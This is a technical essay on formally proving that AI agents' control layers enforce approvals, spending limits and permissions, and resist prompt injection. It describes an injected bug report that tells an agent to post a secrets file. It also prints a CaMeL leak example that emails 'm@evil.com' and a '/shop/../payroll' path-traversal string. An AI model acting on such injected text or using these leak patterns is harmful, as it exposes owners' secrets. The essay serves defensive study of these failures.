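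Santos-Grueiro found 17 security advisories for the coding and assistant agents Cursor, OpenClaw and Claude Code in which an approval did not cover what the product did. In 12 cases the approval had never covered the action, for example because the dialogue box hid some of a command's arguments. In the other five, something changed after the approval, such as the contents of an approved script. The vendors have fixed all 17. Since 13 of the advisories concern OpenClaw, they don't show how common the problem is.

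The check at commit time must find one complete justification. This includes a live approval, up-to-date facts, finished prerequisites and an exact match with the requested effect, and every part must belong to the same approval:

there is an approval *J* such that, for every condition *k*, *J* satisfies *k* now.

A single approval must satisfy every condition. If the check only requires that each condition be satisfied by some approval, it can allow a refund that nobody currently approves. Suppose a supervisor approves a refund when the order's record is at version 7. The customer then returns part of the order, which moves the record to version 8, and the supervisor approves a new refund but soon withdraws it. The old approval is still live, and the withdrawn one names the current version, so the weaker check passes and the refund is paid. This fault appears only in cases that Santos-Grueiro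 constructed, and none of the 17 advisories describes it.

In the Lean model, approvals may disappear and records may change between any two steps. Lean checks that every effect in the log still had a complete, current justification when it occurred. This result assumes that every effect goes through the protected service and that the check and the effect form one step. Of the 139 theorems, 20 are counterexamples that show the limits of a check or an assumption. In one, a service relies on an earlier check and acts after the approval has disappeared.

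Checking an approval and making the payment can't be a single step when one company holds the approvals and another makes the payments. Instead, the approval service can issue a reservation, which permits one exact effect, once, within a time limit *τ*. If the two companies' clocks each differ from the true time by at most *ε*, the payment happens no later than *τ* + 2*ε* after the reservation. But a supervisor can't recall a reservation, so with a limit of ten seconds, a payment can still go through for about ten seconds after its approval is withdrawn.

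Santos-Grueiro also tested whether models notice that an approval no longer holds. Five models did 18 tasks on local services, with instructions to make a change only while the approval and its conditions held. During each run, the owner withdrew the approval or changed another fact it depended on. The model received either no signal, a notice, or a tool for looking up the current status. The table gives the number of runs in which the model completed the task through an unauthorised change when the service did not check whether the change was still authorised. Claude Fable 5 has fewer runs because its provider refused some requests.

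| Model | No signal | Notice | Status tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-7B | 26 of 36 | 15 of 36 | 26 of 36 |
| Gemma 4 31B | 34 of 36 | 10 of 36 | 32 of 36 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 25 of 36 | 1 of 36 | 2 of 36 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 17 of 22 | 0 of 23 | 17 of 27 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 30 of 36 | 0 of 36 | 22 of 36 |

The stronger models obeyed the rule almost perfectly when they were told about the change. Most did not look for changes themselves, except GPT-5.6 Sol, which used the status tool after the change in 34 of its 36 runs. If the approval is lost after the model's last turn, the model cannot respond. With LangChain, a common framework for building agents, 28 writes went ahead after such changes because the framework did not check again before running the approved call. A check added at commit time refused all 28 writes in matching runs. A separate scoring program, which shared no code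 with the check, used the owners' logs to decide which writes were authorized.

An ordinary success score can miss unauthorised changes. Santos-Grueiro added revocable approvals to three customer-service tasks from τ-bench, a benchmark for tool-using agents, and withdrew the approval just before the first change. Four of the five models made the unauthorised change in every run, and the official scorer gave them full marks because it checks only the final database. An agent can also continue its work after a refusal. In 12 coding runs with GPT-5.6 Sol and the two Claude models, the release service refused to publish to production after approval was silently withdrawn. In 11 of those runs, the agent published instead to a test site, which the instructions had named as an alternative and for which it had separate approval.

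The paper's list of what Lean does not prove includes the agent's intent, the cryptographic code, recovery after a crash, undoing changes across several machines, and confidentiality when a request goes out. Lean also does not show that the Python services match the model, or that the approval service correctly records which version each approval was for. If the shop's policy leaves out a relevant fact, such as whether the parcel has come back, the theorem still holds, but the refund may be one the owner would have stopped.

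### Permissions that run out

Some permissions can be used only a limited number of times, such as permission to refund order 123 once. Comparing grants at a single moment therefore isn't enough to prove that permissions never grow. Suppose the refund agent may make one refund and gives each of three helpers a budget of one. No helper's budget exceeds the agent's, but together they can make three refunds unless they all draw on the same counter.

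Widening such a permission can also stop an agent from doing its job. Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues show this with Agenra, whose control layer searches a list of permissions in order and deducts a use from the first one that matches and has uses left. Suppose the first permission allows one refund of order 124 and the second allows one refund of order 123. An agent can refund 123 and then 124. If the owner widens the first permission to cover either order, the refund of 123 uses it up, and the refund of 124 fails because the remaining permission covers only 123. The agent could also refund order 123 twice, which the owner never wanted.

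Choosing permissions more cleverly doesn't solve this in general. Suppose one permission covers a single refund of either 123 or 124, another covers a single refund of either 123 or 125, and the first request is for 123. If the control layer uses up the first permission, it can't later refund 124, and if it uses up the second, it can't later refund 125. In each case the other choice would have allowed the later refund, but the control layer can't know which request will come next. Barth and Mitchell proved this for digital-rights licences, and Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues checked the argument in Lean. The argument assumes that the control layer can't postpone its choice or change it afterwards.

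Agenra therefore treats the survival of existing workflows as a property to prove. Write Runs(*P*) for the call sequences that the control layer admits under a list of permissions *P*, given the same results from outside services. A revision from *P* to *P*′ preserves workflows if

Runs(*P*) ⊆ Runs(*P*′).

The proof relates the usage counters of the old list to those of the new one. Whenever the counters are related and the old list allows a call, the new list must allow it too, and the counters must still be related afterwards. By induction, the new list then allows every sequence of calls that the old list allowed, whatever its length. Raising a limit on uses always meets this condition, and so does adding a permission at the end of the list.

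The researchers tested the method on 51 revisions they wrote themselves, which they don't claim are typical of real maintenance. Lean certified all 21 that preserved every workflow and none of the 30 that lost one. The researchers also tested one real change from Dyad, an open-source app builder, which raised its limit on free messages from five to ten. Lean certified this change, but Dyad also restores a message to the user's allowance if it fails and resets the count after a time. The formal model includes neither rule, so the result covers only successful messages within one period.

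A revision can preserve every workflow and still be unsafe. In another test, an agent was allowed to send a confidential report's public summary once. Raising the limit to two kept every workflow intact but allowed a second send. A reviewer needs one check for what a change newly allows and another for what it breaks.

When permissions can run out, a new prohibition can also lead the control layer to approve a later request it would otherwise have refused, even though the prohibition allows no new kind of request. For example, banning a particular $900 refund can leave room in the shop's daily limit for a later $200 refund.

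### Checking a policy against every request

Owners revise their rules, and nobody can try out every request under the old and new versions. An SMT solver can compare the versions directly. An engineer translates both into formulas and asks for a request *q* such that

New(*q*) and not Old(*q*).

If no such request exists, the new policy allows nothing that the old one refused. For order 123, the solver finds no action and time that the helper's grant permits but the refund agent's grant does not. If somebody had set the helper's grant to expire at 18:00, the solver would return an example, such as reading the order at 17:30. *What we have learned applying formal methods to control AI agents* (Watson, 2026) applies these queries, called containment queries, to permission changes in long-running agents.

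Cedar, a policy language from Amazon Web Services (AWS), suits this kind of analysis because its designers kept it simple enough to translate exactly into logical formulas. It allows a request only if at least one permitting rule matches in full and no prohibition matches. Cutler and colleagues introduced Cedar in a 2024 paper, modeled it in Lean, and proved properties of its design. The program that makes decisions in practice is written in Rust, and the developers compare its answers with the Lean model's on many random inputs. AWS uses Cedar to control agents in its Bedrock AgentCore service.

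A solver doesn't always reach a verdict, and AWS's *Prove it part 2* explains that a sound system may answer "I cannot determine this" rather than guess. A careful owner would hold back a policy that gets this answer. Comparing policies one request at a time also misses permissions that run out. In tests by Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues, the widened permission passed a check that the new list still covered every individual action, even though two workflows no longer worked.

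Google announced a verifier for its Common Expression Language (CEL) on 18 August 2026. Many cloud systems use CEL for access rules, and AI agents increasingly write those rules. According to Digital Magazin's *Google lässt den Z3-Theorembeweiser über KI-geschriebene Zugriffsregeln wachen*, Google's Sean Huh warned that an agent may fit a rule to the existing tests and fail on real traffic. The verifier passes the rule to Z3, an SMT solver from Microsoft Research. One of Google's examples comes from an engineer who assumes that every request uses either a port up to 80 or a port above 1024, a port being the number that directs network traffic to a particular program:

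request.port > 1024 || request.port <= 80

The two vertical bars mean "or". The verifier can check whether the expression is true for every possible port. It is false for every port from 81 to 1024, because both halves are false. That range includes 443, the standard port for encrypted web traffic, and a test suite containing only ports 80 and 8080 would not reveal the gap. The engineer still has to decide whether the rule should admit or reject those ports.

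In December 2026, AWS previewed Greenlight, which drafts rules for agents as well as checking them. According to Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (2026), the service blocks all tools and network destinations until a team allows them. A language model drafts rules from the company's procedures, security standards and logs of earlier tool calls. Greenlight then uses automated reasoning to check for conflicting rules and for routes to resources outside the agent's approved access. The team can also see which recorded calls a proposed rule would have blocked. The approved rules run outside the agent, where the agent can't change them. AWS plans to support systems with several agents but doesn't yet, so the preview doesn't prove anything about delegation.

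ITWeb's *AWS creates gateway to 'trust' AI agents* reports AWS chief executive Matt Garman's claim that the logic proves there is "no chance of misinterpretation" and no way for an agent to break a specified rule. TechRadar's *'It's truly unlike anything else out there today'* quotes AWS as saying that agents using Greenlight can be trusted even with high-stakes tasks. AWS's Shawn Bice was more cautious. He told Computertrends that the proof holds only for the policies and system that the organisation has specified and modelled, and that each organisation must decide for itself which outcomes matter.

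Bice's description is the accurate one. Greenlight's users can state their rules in ordinary language, and the proof starts only after software has translated them into logic. If the software mistranslates a rule, the proof can be correct but apply to a rule the user didn't intend. Garman also argued for the product using the example of an agent that errs in 0.1% of its steps and so completes a 1,000-step task only about 35% of the time. That error rate includes every kind of mistake, but the proof rules out only those that break a written rule.

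### Leaks through a permitted channel

Even if the shop has narrowed every grant, checks approvals at the moment of payment and has used a solver to compare its policies, the refund agent still needs permission to send text to customers so it can answer them. If the control layer checks only who sends a message, for what purpose and to whom, it makes the same decision whether the text is "Your refund is on its way" or another customer's home address.

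Tran-Truong and colleagues state this observation as a proposition. It covers any monitor whose decision depends on the sender, purpose, data labels, operation, sink and chain of grants, but not on the content or quantity of the data. For every sink that some agent may use and outsiders can observe, the monitor lets arbitrary secret content through in at least one run. The proof starts from a harmless message that the monitor permits. If the secret replaces the message's content and everything else stays the same, nothing the decision depends on has changed, so the monitor permits the new message too, and an outsider reads it. Stricter attenuation can't help while the sink remains permitted.

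The tests match the proposition. The researchers attacked five workflows in 45 runs, using a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, whose agents could talk to each other and try again after a refusal. Without the monitor, 38 runs leaked, compared with nine when it was on. Those nine were all the runs of one workflow, in which an agent reviews code that contains a secret security flaw and posts its comments where the public can read them. In the other four workflows, where the permitted sink was private, nothing leaked with the monitor on.

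Filtering messages by content stops such leaks but also blocks legitimate messages. In a separate set of 26 attacks, DelegateGuard let three leaks through, again all in code review, while a filter that searched outgoing messages for the secret let none through. But the filter also blocked four of the five legitimate messages, because they had to carry the protected data to the user or into an internal record. The researchers therefore recommend combining control over permissions with explicit rules about which content may leave through a public sink. The shop could go further and limit the agent to four fixed replies. Each reply's wording would then carry at most two bits of information, although the agent could still signal more through the number and timing of its messages.

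## Proving that no sequence of actions breaks a rule

An agent can have permission for every refund it pays and still exceed a $1,000 daily limit, because the limit applies to the day's total. Proving that the limit holds therefore requires an invariant that remains true whatever order requests, payments and failures happen in.

### Two refunds of $600

So far the control layer has checked and paid each refund in a single step. Payment services can be slow, so a real control layer may approve a refund now and pay it later. Let *p* be the amount paid so far today, and suppose the control layer approves a refund of *a* whenever *p* + *a* ≤ 1,000. Two customers ask for $600 each while *p* is zero. The control layer approves both requests, because no money has gone out yet and 0 + 600 ≤ 1,000 each time. Both payments go through, and the shop has paid $1,200.

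An attempted proof exposes the mistake. The obvious invariant to try is *p* ≤ 1,000. It holds at the start, and approving a refund doesn't change *p*. But paying an approved refund adds its amount, *a*, to *p*, and *p* ≤ 1,000 doesn't limit what the control layer has already approved. If *p* is 600 and another approved refund of $600 is waiting, paying it raises *p* to 1,200.

The repair is to make each approval reserve money. Let *r* be the total that the control layer has approved but not yet paid or cancelled. Four kinds of step can now change the state:

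| Step | Condition | New *p* | New *r* |
|---|---|---|---|
| Approve *a* | *a* > 0 and *p* + *r* + *a* ≤ 1,000 | *p* | *r* + *a* |
| Pay *a* | 0 < *a* ≤ *r* | *p* + *a* | *r* − *a* |
| Cancel *a* | 0 < *a* ≤ *r* | *p* | *r* − *a* |
| Midnight | none | 0 | *r* |

The control layer now refuses the other $600 request, because 0 + 600 + 600 is more than 1,000.

In the repaired program *p* never exceeds 1,000, yet the proof of *p* ≤ 1,000 still fails at the same place. Induction considers every state in which the candidate is true, including states that the program can never reach. The state *p* = 600, *r* = 600 satisfies *p* ≤ 1,000, and paying the reserved $600 leads to $1,200. An SMT solver would return this state as a counterexample, and the engineer would have to work out whether the program can get there. The old program could approve both refunds and reach the equivalent state. The new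 one can't, so the invariant needs a further condition that excludes it:

*p* ≥ 0,  *r* ≥ 0  and  *p* + *r* ≤ 1,000.

All three parts hold at the start, when *p* and *r* are zero. Approving a refund raises *r*, and the condition in the table keeps the sum within 1,000. Paying moves money from *r* to *p* and leaves the sum unchanged. Cancelling lowers the sum. At midnight *p* drops to zero, which cannot raise the sum because *p* was not negative. The limit follows because *r* ≥ 0 gives *p* ≤ *p* + *r* ≤ 1,000.

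The last inequality in the proof requires *r* ≥ 0, because *p* = 1,500 and *r* = −500 also add up to 1,000. The midnight step requires *p* ≥ 0. If the program didn't require amounts to be positive, it could approve −$500 and then $1,500, leaving *r* at 1,000. Paying the −$500 would make *p* = −500 and *r* = 1,500. Midnight would reset *p* to zero, and the program would then pay $1,500 on the new day. The schema prevents this by banning negative amounts.

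### The statement in Lean

In Lean, the definitions and the two theorems look roughly like this, with the proofs left out:

```
structure State where
  paid : Int
  reserved : Int

def Inv (s : State) : Prop :=
  0 ≤ s.paid ∧ 0 ≤ s.reserved ∧ s.paid + s.reserved ≤ 1000

theorem keeps (s t : State) (h : Inv s) (st : Step s t) : Inv t

theorem limit (s : State) (h : Reachable s) : s.paid ≤ 1000
```

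The first three lines define a state as a pair of whole numbers, which may be negative. The next two define the invariant, where ∧ means "and" and `Prop` marks a statement that can be true or false. The theorem `keeps` takes any two states *s* and *t*, a proof `h` that the invariant holds in *s*, and a proof `st` that one of the table's four steps leads from *s* to *t*. Its conclusion is that the invariant holds in *t*. The case for each step is simple arithmetic, which Lean can prove automatically. The theorem `limit` covers every state the program can reach from zero in any number of steps. Its proof applies `keeps` once for each step and then drops `reserved` from the sum.

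The midnight row also defines a day in the theorem, so a refund approved on Monday and paid on Tuesday counts toward Tuesday's limit. A different invariant can rule out the double payout around midnight. Reservoir, the index of Lean packages, describes a request limiter for a web server, verified in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier. The limiter's invariant bounds the number of requests in any sliding window of time. The same file contains a run in which a fixed-window counter admits twice the limit. The proof still assumes that the clock never goes backwards and that the server updates each user's record in one indivisible step.

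### Shared budgets in practice

The table treats "approve" as one step, so the program must check the sum and reserve the money before any other request can read the old values. In *Token Budgets*, Khan (2026) tested what happens without this protection when agents spend money on calls to a model. When several helpers drew on one unprotected counter, they overspent in all 30 runs. With a lock, which lets only one helper at a time read and change the counter, they overspent in none of 30. Khan also collected 63 confirmed budget overruns from public reports on 21 agent projects. These show that overruns recur, but not how common they are, because Khan searched only for overruns.

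Khan's own remedy is a library in Rust, a language whose compiler tracks the ownership of each value. If a programmer copies a budget, or keeps using it after passing it to a helper, the program doesn't compile. A correctly locked counter enforces the same limit, but the library keeps these mistakes out of running systems.

Unlike the amount of a refund, the price of a model call is unknown until the reply is complete. Khan's library therefore reserves an estimate, and the spending limit holds only if the estimate is never too low. The default method typically reserves four to six times the actual cost, which ties up money that the agent could have used. Khan does not claim the guarantee for models that bill for hidden reasoning of unpredictable length.

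### Containment verification

An agent framework, the software that runs the loop between a model and its tools, has far more state than two numbers. Moon and Varshney (2026), in *Containment Verification*, proved rules of this kind for PocketFlow, a minimal framework in which a developer describes an agent's work as a graph. Each node does part of the work and emits an action, and PocketFlow follows the connection labeled with that action. They chose PocketFlow because larger frameworks such as LangChain contain a similar loop.

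Their version of PocketFlow accepts four kinds of action and enforces three rules. The agent may read files only inside a chosen workspace folder, may call only tools on an approved list, and may take no more than a set number of steps. When the agent proposes anything else, the framework records a step with no effect.

Like Metere's approach, the proof in *Containment Verification* assumes nothing about the model's choices. It represents the model in Dafny as a method with no body, whose declaration fixes only the type of its result. The theorem covers every typed action, but the proof excludes the code that turns the model's text into an action. The result is therefore narrower than the enforcement for "every possible AI output" promised in the abstract.

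The main theorem is about refinement, which means that a detailed program does only what a simpler description allows. The simpler description is the abstract model, and the detailed one is the operational model. Both receive the same actions. Each step starts in a state *s*, takes an action *a*, produces a boundary event *e* such as a file read, and ends in a state *s*′. A policy Π(*s*, *a*, *e*, *s*′) determines whether a step is acceptable, and each model has its own version of it. The operational model refines the abstract one if engineers can define which states and events correspond so that:

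- the two starting states correspond;
- from corresponding states, every step of the operational model has a matching step of the abstract model with the same action, a corresponding event and a corresponding new state;
- whenever the abstract step satisfies the abstract policy, the matching operational step satisfies the operational policy.

By the theorem, if the abstract model also keeps its policy under every possible sequence of actions, then the operational model keeps its own policy under every sequence too. The proof starts with an arbitrary run of the operational model. The starting states correspond, and each step has a match, so by induction there is an abstract run with exactly the same actions. That run keeps the abstract policy by assumption, so by the last condition, applied at each step, the operational run keeps the operational policy.

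In the refund agent example, the table with *p* and *r* is an abstract model. The shop's actual program might store a row in a database for each refund, marked "approved" or "paid". A database state corresponds to (*p*, *r*) when today's paid rows add up to *p* and the approved rows add up to *r*. When the program changes a $60 row from "approved" to "paid", the abstract model takes the step "Pay 60". This division of labour is useful because engineers can prove the limit once for the two numbers, then show separately that the database always corresponds to them. If they later reorganise the database, they have to redo only the proof of correspondence.

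Moon and Varshney had to strengthen their invariant, as was necessary for the refund limit. Besides bounding the number of steps, it requires, for example, that the length of the recorded history match the step counter. A corollary extends the theorem to the deployed system, provided every outside effect appears as a modelled event, which again requires complete mediation. The trusted base also includes the policy, the definitions of which states and events correspond, and Dafny's verifier and compiler.

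In the published proof, the workspace rule requires each recorded path to start with the path of the workspace folder. If that test compares plain text and the workspace folder is `/shop`, it accepts `/shop/../payroll`, which leads out of the folder because the two dots mean "go up one folder". Unless other code resolves such paths first, the agent could read the payroll even though the theorem is true.

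### A rule about an empty list

Moon and Varshney used language models to write most of the formal work. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the models, properties and proofs. A language model that can see the program may write a specification that merely describes what the program does. The program would then satisfy the specification even if the code were wrong. The researchers therefore set up an information barrier, so the step that derives the safety property receives the interface and a general template but not the program's code.

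Four runs tested the system with and without the barrier on two agents, one that reads files and one that looks up documents before answering. Dafny accepted every final proof, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each path through an agent's graph. Each run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens. The runs without the barrier used 25% to 56% more than those with it, because the language model also had to read the code.

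Before the final proof, each specification had to pass three tests. The resolution test checks that the Dafny text parses and type-checks. In the vacuity test, the software reduces the invariant to a basic requirement that states be well formed and empties the supporting proofs. Verification must then fail, because success would mean the theorem did not depend on the invariant. In the discrimination test, a language model adds a plausible mistake to the proof file, and verification must again fail.

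Every specification passed all three tests, but one contained a rule that restricted nothing. The document agent keeps a list of the documents it has read and may read only approved ones. The template had fields for tool calls and approved tools, but none for documents. With the barrier in place, Claude used the tool fields for documents, treating each document read as a tool call and the approved documents as approved tools. The names were odd, but the rule did restrict the agent. Without the barrier, Claude could see that documents and tools were different things, and it left the list of tool calls unchanged at every step. The list stayed empty throughout every run, so the rule had nothing to check.

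The specification required that every recorded tool call be on the approved list:

for every *c* in *toolCalls*,  *c* ∈ *allowedTools*.

When *toolCalls* is empty, this statement is true whatever the agent does, so the proof succeeded even though no rule covered the documents. The tests missed the fault because their alterations damaged other parts of the proof, which failed as they should. None of the tests checked whether each rule had anything to apply to. Moon and Varshney recommend also checking that every field a safety rule mentions is non-empty in some state the program can reach. This example shows that a successful proof and three sensible tests can miss such a rule, though a single example can't show how often language models produce them.

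### No effect before a check

The order of events can also be a safety property. *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance* (McCann, 2026) uses Rocq to prove that programs on Mashin, an AI workflow platform made by McCann's company, produce no outside effect before a permission check. Rocq accepted the whole development of 454 theorems.

The proof centres on a predicate called `gov_safe`, which applies to a program together with a flag. The flag records whether a check has taken place, and it starts as false. Four rules define which programs are safe:

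- A program that has finished is safe.
- A step of internal computation is safe if the rest of the program is safe with the same flag.
- A check is safe if, for either answer, the rest of the program is safe with the flag set to true.
- An outside effect is safe if the flag is already true and the rest of the program is safe.

McCann proves a separate lemma in three lines: a program whose next step is an unchecked effect fails the predicate. If such a program were safe, one of the four rules would have to apply, but the only rule for effects requires the flag to be true, and here it is false. The lemma shows that the predicate rejects some programs, without which the main theorem would be worthless.

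The programs may run forever, so McCann defines the predicate by coinduction: a program counts as safe unless some finite series of steps leads to a violation. The main theorem states that every program is safe when Mashin's governance operator runs it. The operator handles each request by performing four checks, then the effect, and then three steps that record or review it. The 213-line proof follows this sequence and shows that each effect comes after a check has set the flag.

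A check sets the flag to true even if the answer is no, and nothing sets it back to false. A program would therefore satisfy `gov_safe` if it asked whether it could refund order 123, was refused and paid anyway, or if it made a thousand payments after one check. McCann's operator does neither, because it repeats the checks for every request and performs the effect only if they pass. A shop owner would need both `gov_safe` and the separate theorem about Mashin's interpreter that a refused request causes no outside effect.

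### Safe and useless

When a check refuses a request, McCann's operator loops forever without doing anything. The loop never reaches an effect, so it never reaches an unchecked one, and McCann describes it as "vacuously safe". For the same reason, `gov_safe` still holds if the operator refuses every request and the program never does anything.

A refund agent whose control layer rejects every request also satisfies every safety property that only forbids effects. A deadline for answers would rule out the endless loop, but not a layer that immediately rejects every request.

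To exclude such a layer, engineers can also prove when it must say yes:

*a* > 0  and  *p* + *r* + *a* ≤ 1,000  ⇒  the control layer approves *a*.

This theorem fails for a layer that refuses everything, but it doesn't guarantee that the shop can keep working. If a programmer forgets the "Cancel" step, then whenever the payment service rejects a refund, the money stays reserved. Once $1,000 has built up this way, the control layer refuses every request from then on, because *r* doesn't change at midnight, yet both theorems remain true. Cancelling too early is also dangerous. If a $600 payment succeeds but its confirmation gets lost, and the control layer cancels the reservation, it can approve another $600 and exceed the limit. The control layer should cancel only when the payment service confirms that the payment won't go through.

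Customers need every reservation to end eventually in payment or cancellation. This is a liveness property, which an invariant can't establish. The usual method is to find a quantity that falls with every step and cannot fall forever. *Bounded Loops* (Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj, 2026) uses this method for workflows in which a failure at a late stage can send work back to an earlier one for repair. If each stage has its own allowance of repairs, two stages can keep restoring each other's attempts forever. The paper instead gives the whole workflow a single allowance of *R* repairs. Each repair reduces the number of repairs left, and each attempt between repairs reduces the number of attempts left, so the workflow must end. If the stages' attempt limits add up to *M*, the workflow makes at most (*R* + 1) × *M* attempts. For example, three stages with four attempts each and two repairs can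 make at most 36. The workflow may still end in failure, because the theorem shows only that it ends.

### How to detect a vacuous specification

Researchers have known about vacuous specifications for decades. Bhardwaj and colleagues take the term from 2001 work by Beer and others on model checking, the automatic search through a system's states. In their own published catalogue of agent workflows, Bhardwaj and colleagues found 47 checks that passed when the thing they were supposed to examine was missing. All 47 had already passed review. An engineer can look for such faults in three steps, shown here on the refund limit.

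The engineer gives an example of an allowed action by producing a complete run in which the control layer approves $60 and pays it, ending with *p* = 60 and *r* = 0. This run shows that the layer doesn't refuse everything. It also shows that the field in the rule gets filled, a check the document agent's specification would have failed. Finally, it shows that the theorem's assumptions can all be true together. If they contradicted each other, any conclusion would follow from them, and a proof assistant would accept a proof of it.

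Contradictory assumptions are easy to overlook because each can look reasonable. *Beyond LLM Judge* (2026), which describes a system for translating mathematics into formal statements, reports a case from a reference work on mathematical functions. A translation of the formal statement back into ordinary mathematics appeared faithful, but the statement's assumptions about the order and completeness of a list of zeros could not both hold. The system now replaces a theorem's conclusion with a meaningless placeholder and reruns the proof. If the proof still succeeds, it never depended on the conclusion, and the assumptions probably contradict each other. Such automatic checks have limits. *DafnyCert* (2026), a tool that measures how much Dafny specifications demand, rejects specifications that Dafny can show to be vacuous, but it cannot rule out every vacuous specification.

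The engineer uses examples of forbidden actions to show that the control layer refuses a $61 payment when it has already paid $940, and that the specification itself rejects a day with payments of $600 and $500. These examples are needed because a specification that no run can violate imposes no requirement. One of the faulty checks that Bhardwaj and colleagues found was supposed to catch invented legal citations. It built its search pattern from a list of known law reports, so it passed text that cited a law report that didn't exist. Testing the check on a single invented citation from outside the list would have revealed the fault.

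An engineer can check whether the theorem captures the rule by altering the program and running the proof again. If the engineer removes *r* from the condition for approval, the proof fails at the "Approve" step, as it should. If the engineer instead deletes the instruction that adds a payment to *p*, the Lean proof above still succeeds, because the theorem restricts only the stored number, not the payments themselves. If the engineer then adds a list of today's payments to the state and states the limit as a bound on their sum, the proof correctly fails.

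An altered program that still passes isn't always a sign of trouble. If the engineer changes ≤ to < in the approval condition, the control layer refuses the refund that would bring the total to exactly $1,000. The limit still holds, so the proof should succeed. Changes that only make the layer stricter always pass a safety proof, but the theorem about when the layer must approve should fail.

Software can automate part of the search for empty specifications. *Verified but Vacuous* (2026) describes a quick test for Dafny programs that come with a separate specification. A method passes if at least one of the conditions that must hold when it finishes refers to that specification. In an internal audit, about 27% of components that Dafny had verified failed this test. For a different system, which wasn't designed to keep programs and specifications separate, the figure was about 98%. Failing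 the test doesn't always mean that a specification is empty, and a component can pass by referring to one that is trivially true.

The result also depends on which alterations are tested. After Bhardwaj and colleagues repaired their faulty checks, the checks accepted none of 209 deliberately damaged pieces of work. When the engineers damaged the work in new ways, the same checks accepted 23.3%. The engineers had used the earlier kinds of damage to find and repair the faults, so a perfect score on those was little evidence that the checks would catch other kinds of mistakes.

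## Proving that untrusted text does not choose the actions

A refund agent can keep every rule described so far and still follow a stranger's instructions. Suppose a customer writes that her lamp arrived broken and forwards the delivery firm's reply. Somebody has hidden an instruction in that reply to refund every order on her account, and the agent refunds both the lamp and the mug. Both refund requests are well formed, both orders belong to the customer, and the total of $92 is far below the daily limit, but nobody authorized to request the mug's refund did so.

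In a prompt injection, a model follows an instruction in text it should have treated only as data. Microsoft's documentation for its Agent Framework gives the example of an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. An attacker files an ordinary-looking report with a footer containing a fake system message, with instructions to read a file of secrets and post its contents as a public comment. The model receives the report and footer as one string, and nothing in it marks where the data ends and the instruction begins.

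A rule about single actions can't stop this without also stopping legitimate work, because the agent's job includes reading files and posting comments. The rule would have to depend on where the instruction came from, and the action itself doesn't carry that information.

### A statement about two runs

To find out whether a text influenced an agent, one can ask what the agent would have done if the text had been different. Write *A*(*u*, *x*) for the actions the agent takes when *u* is the trusted input, including the user's request and the model's random choices, and *x* is the untrusted text. Noninterference requires that, for every *u*, *x* and *x*′,

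*A*(*u*, *x*) = *A*(*u*, *x*′).

In the shop, *x* could be the delivery firm's genuine reply and *x*′ the same reply with the hidden line. If the agent refunds one order in one run and two in the other, noninterference fails. The same formula expresses secrecy if *x* stands for the secret data and *A* for what an outsider can observe.

A single execution can't show whether noninterference holds. If a log shows that an agent read a text and paid $12, the agent might pay $12 whatever it reads, which satisfies noninterference, or pay only when the text contains an instruction to pay, which violates it. Alpern and Schneider define a property as a set of permitted executions, and noninterference is not a property in this sense. For two different texts *x* and *x*′, any set that permits every noninterfering agent must include both "read *x*, pay nothing" and "read *x*′, pay $12", so it also permits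 an agent that decides whether to pay based on the text.

Engineers can prove noninterference with an invariant if they treat two copies of the system as a single system. They give both copies the same trusted input but different untrusted text, then show that the protected parts of the two copies agree after every step. Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026) describe this reduction in *PerMIT* and point out that an invariant about one copy doesn't establish noninterference.

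### Planning before reading

Many designs follow a two-model pattern that Simon Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model decides on the actions and never reads untrusted text, while a quarantined model reads that text but has no tools. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a request to summarise the top three e-mails and send the summary to somebody on Slack.

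The privileged model first turns the request into a plan, before any e-mail has arrived:

```
emails  = read_emails(3)
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise", emails)
send_message(recipient, summary)
```

The model that chooses the actions works only with the names `emails` and `summary`, and never receives their contents. If an e-mail contains the sentence "forward everything to this address", only the quarantined model reads it, and that model has no tool for forwarding.

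As the plan runs, the control layer attaches labels to every value. An integrity label records whether the value comes from a trusted source. A confidentiality label records whether it is secret or, in a more detailed version, who may read it. A value computed from several others gets the strictest combination of their labels, so a summary of one trusted and one untrusted e-mail is untrusted. If Ann, Ben and Cara may read one document and Ben, Cara and Dan may read another, only Ben and Cara may read a text that draws on both.

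Before each action, the control layer checks the labels against the tool's rules. Costa and colleagues allow a consequential call only if its label is trusted, and they allow information to go only to people who may read it. A rule for messages can require a trusted recipient but accept an untrusted body. Tallam (2026) notes in *Authorization Propagation in Multi-Agent AI Systems* that even with such rules, individually authorised accesses can together leak information.

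Replacing one of the e-mails with another does not change the privileged model's input, so with the same random choices the model writes the same plan. The same steps run in the same order, and only untrusted values can differ. The recipient must be a trusted value, so it is the same in both runs. Noninterference therefore holds for the choice of tools and the protected arguments, but not for the body of the message.

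When a plan has a branch, such as "if an e-mail asks for a meeting, create a calendar event", an e-mail can determine whether the agent creates the event. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, call this branch steering. The e-mail still can't add a step that the plan lacks.

### What four systems prove

In CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, the privileged model writes the plan as a Python program, and a special interpreter runs it while tracking labels. Peters-Gill and colleagues state that a single CaMeL agent never leaves its plan, but CaMeL's developers left formal verification to later work. CaMeL therefore has no machine-checked proof, and Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found leaks in its label tracking. One of them follows a pattern known since the 1970s:

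```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The balance is secret. CaMeL marks a variable as secret when the program assigns to it inside a branch that depends on a secret. If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and is marked secret. The program then skips the assignment to `rich`, which stays true and public. The e-mail therefore goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no e-mail goes out. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is above the threshold. CaMeL also retries failed plans in a loop outside the interpreter, and an attacker can use this loop to extract a whole secret one bit at a time.

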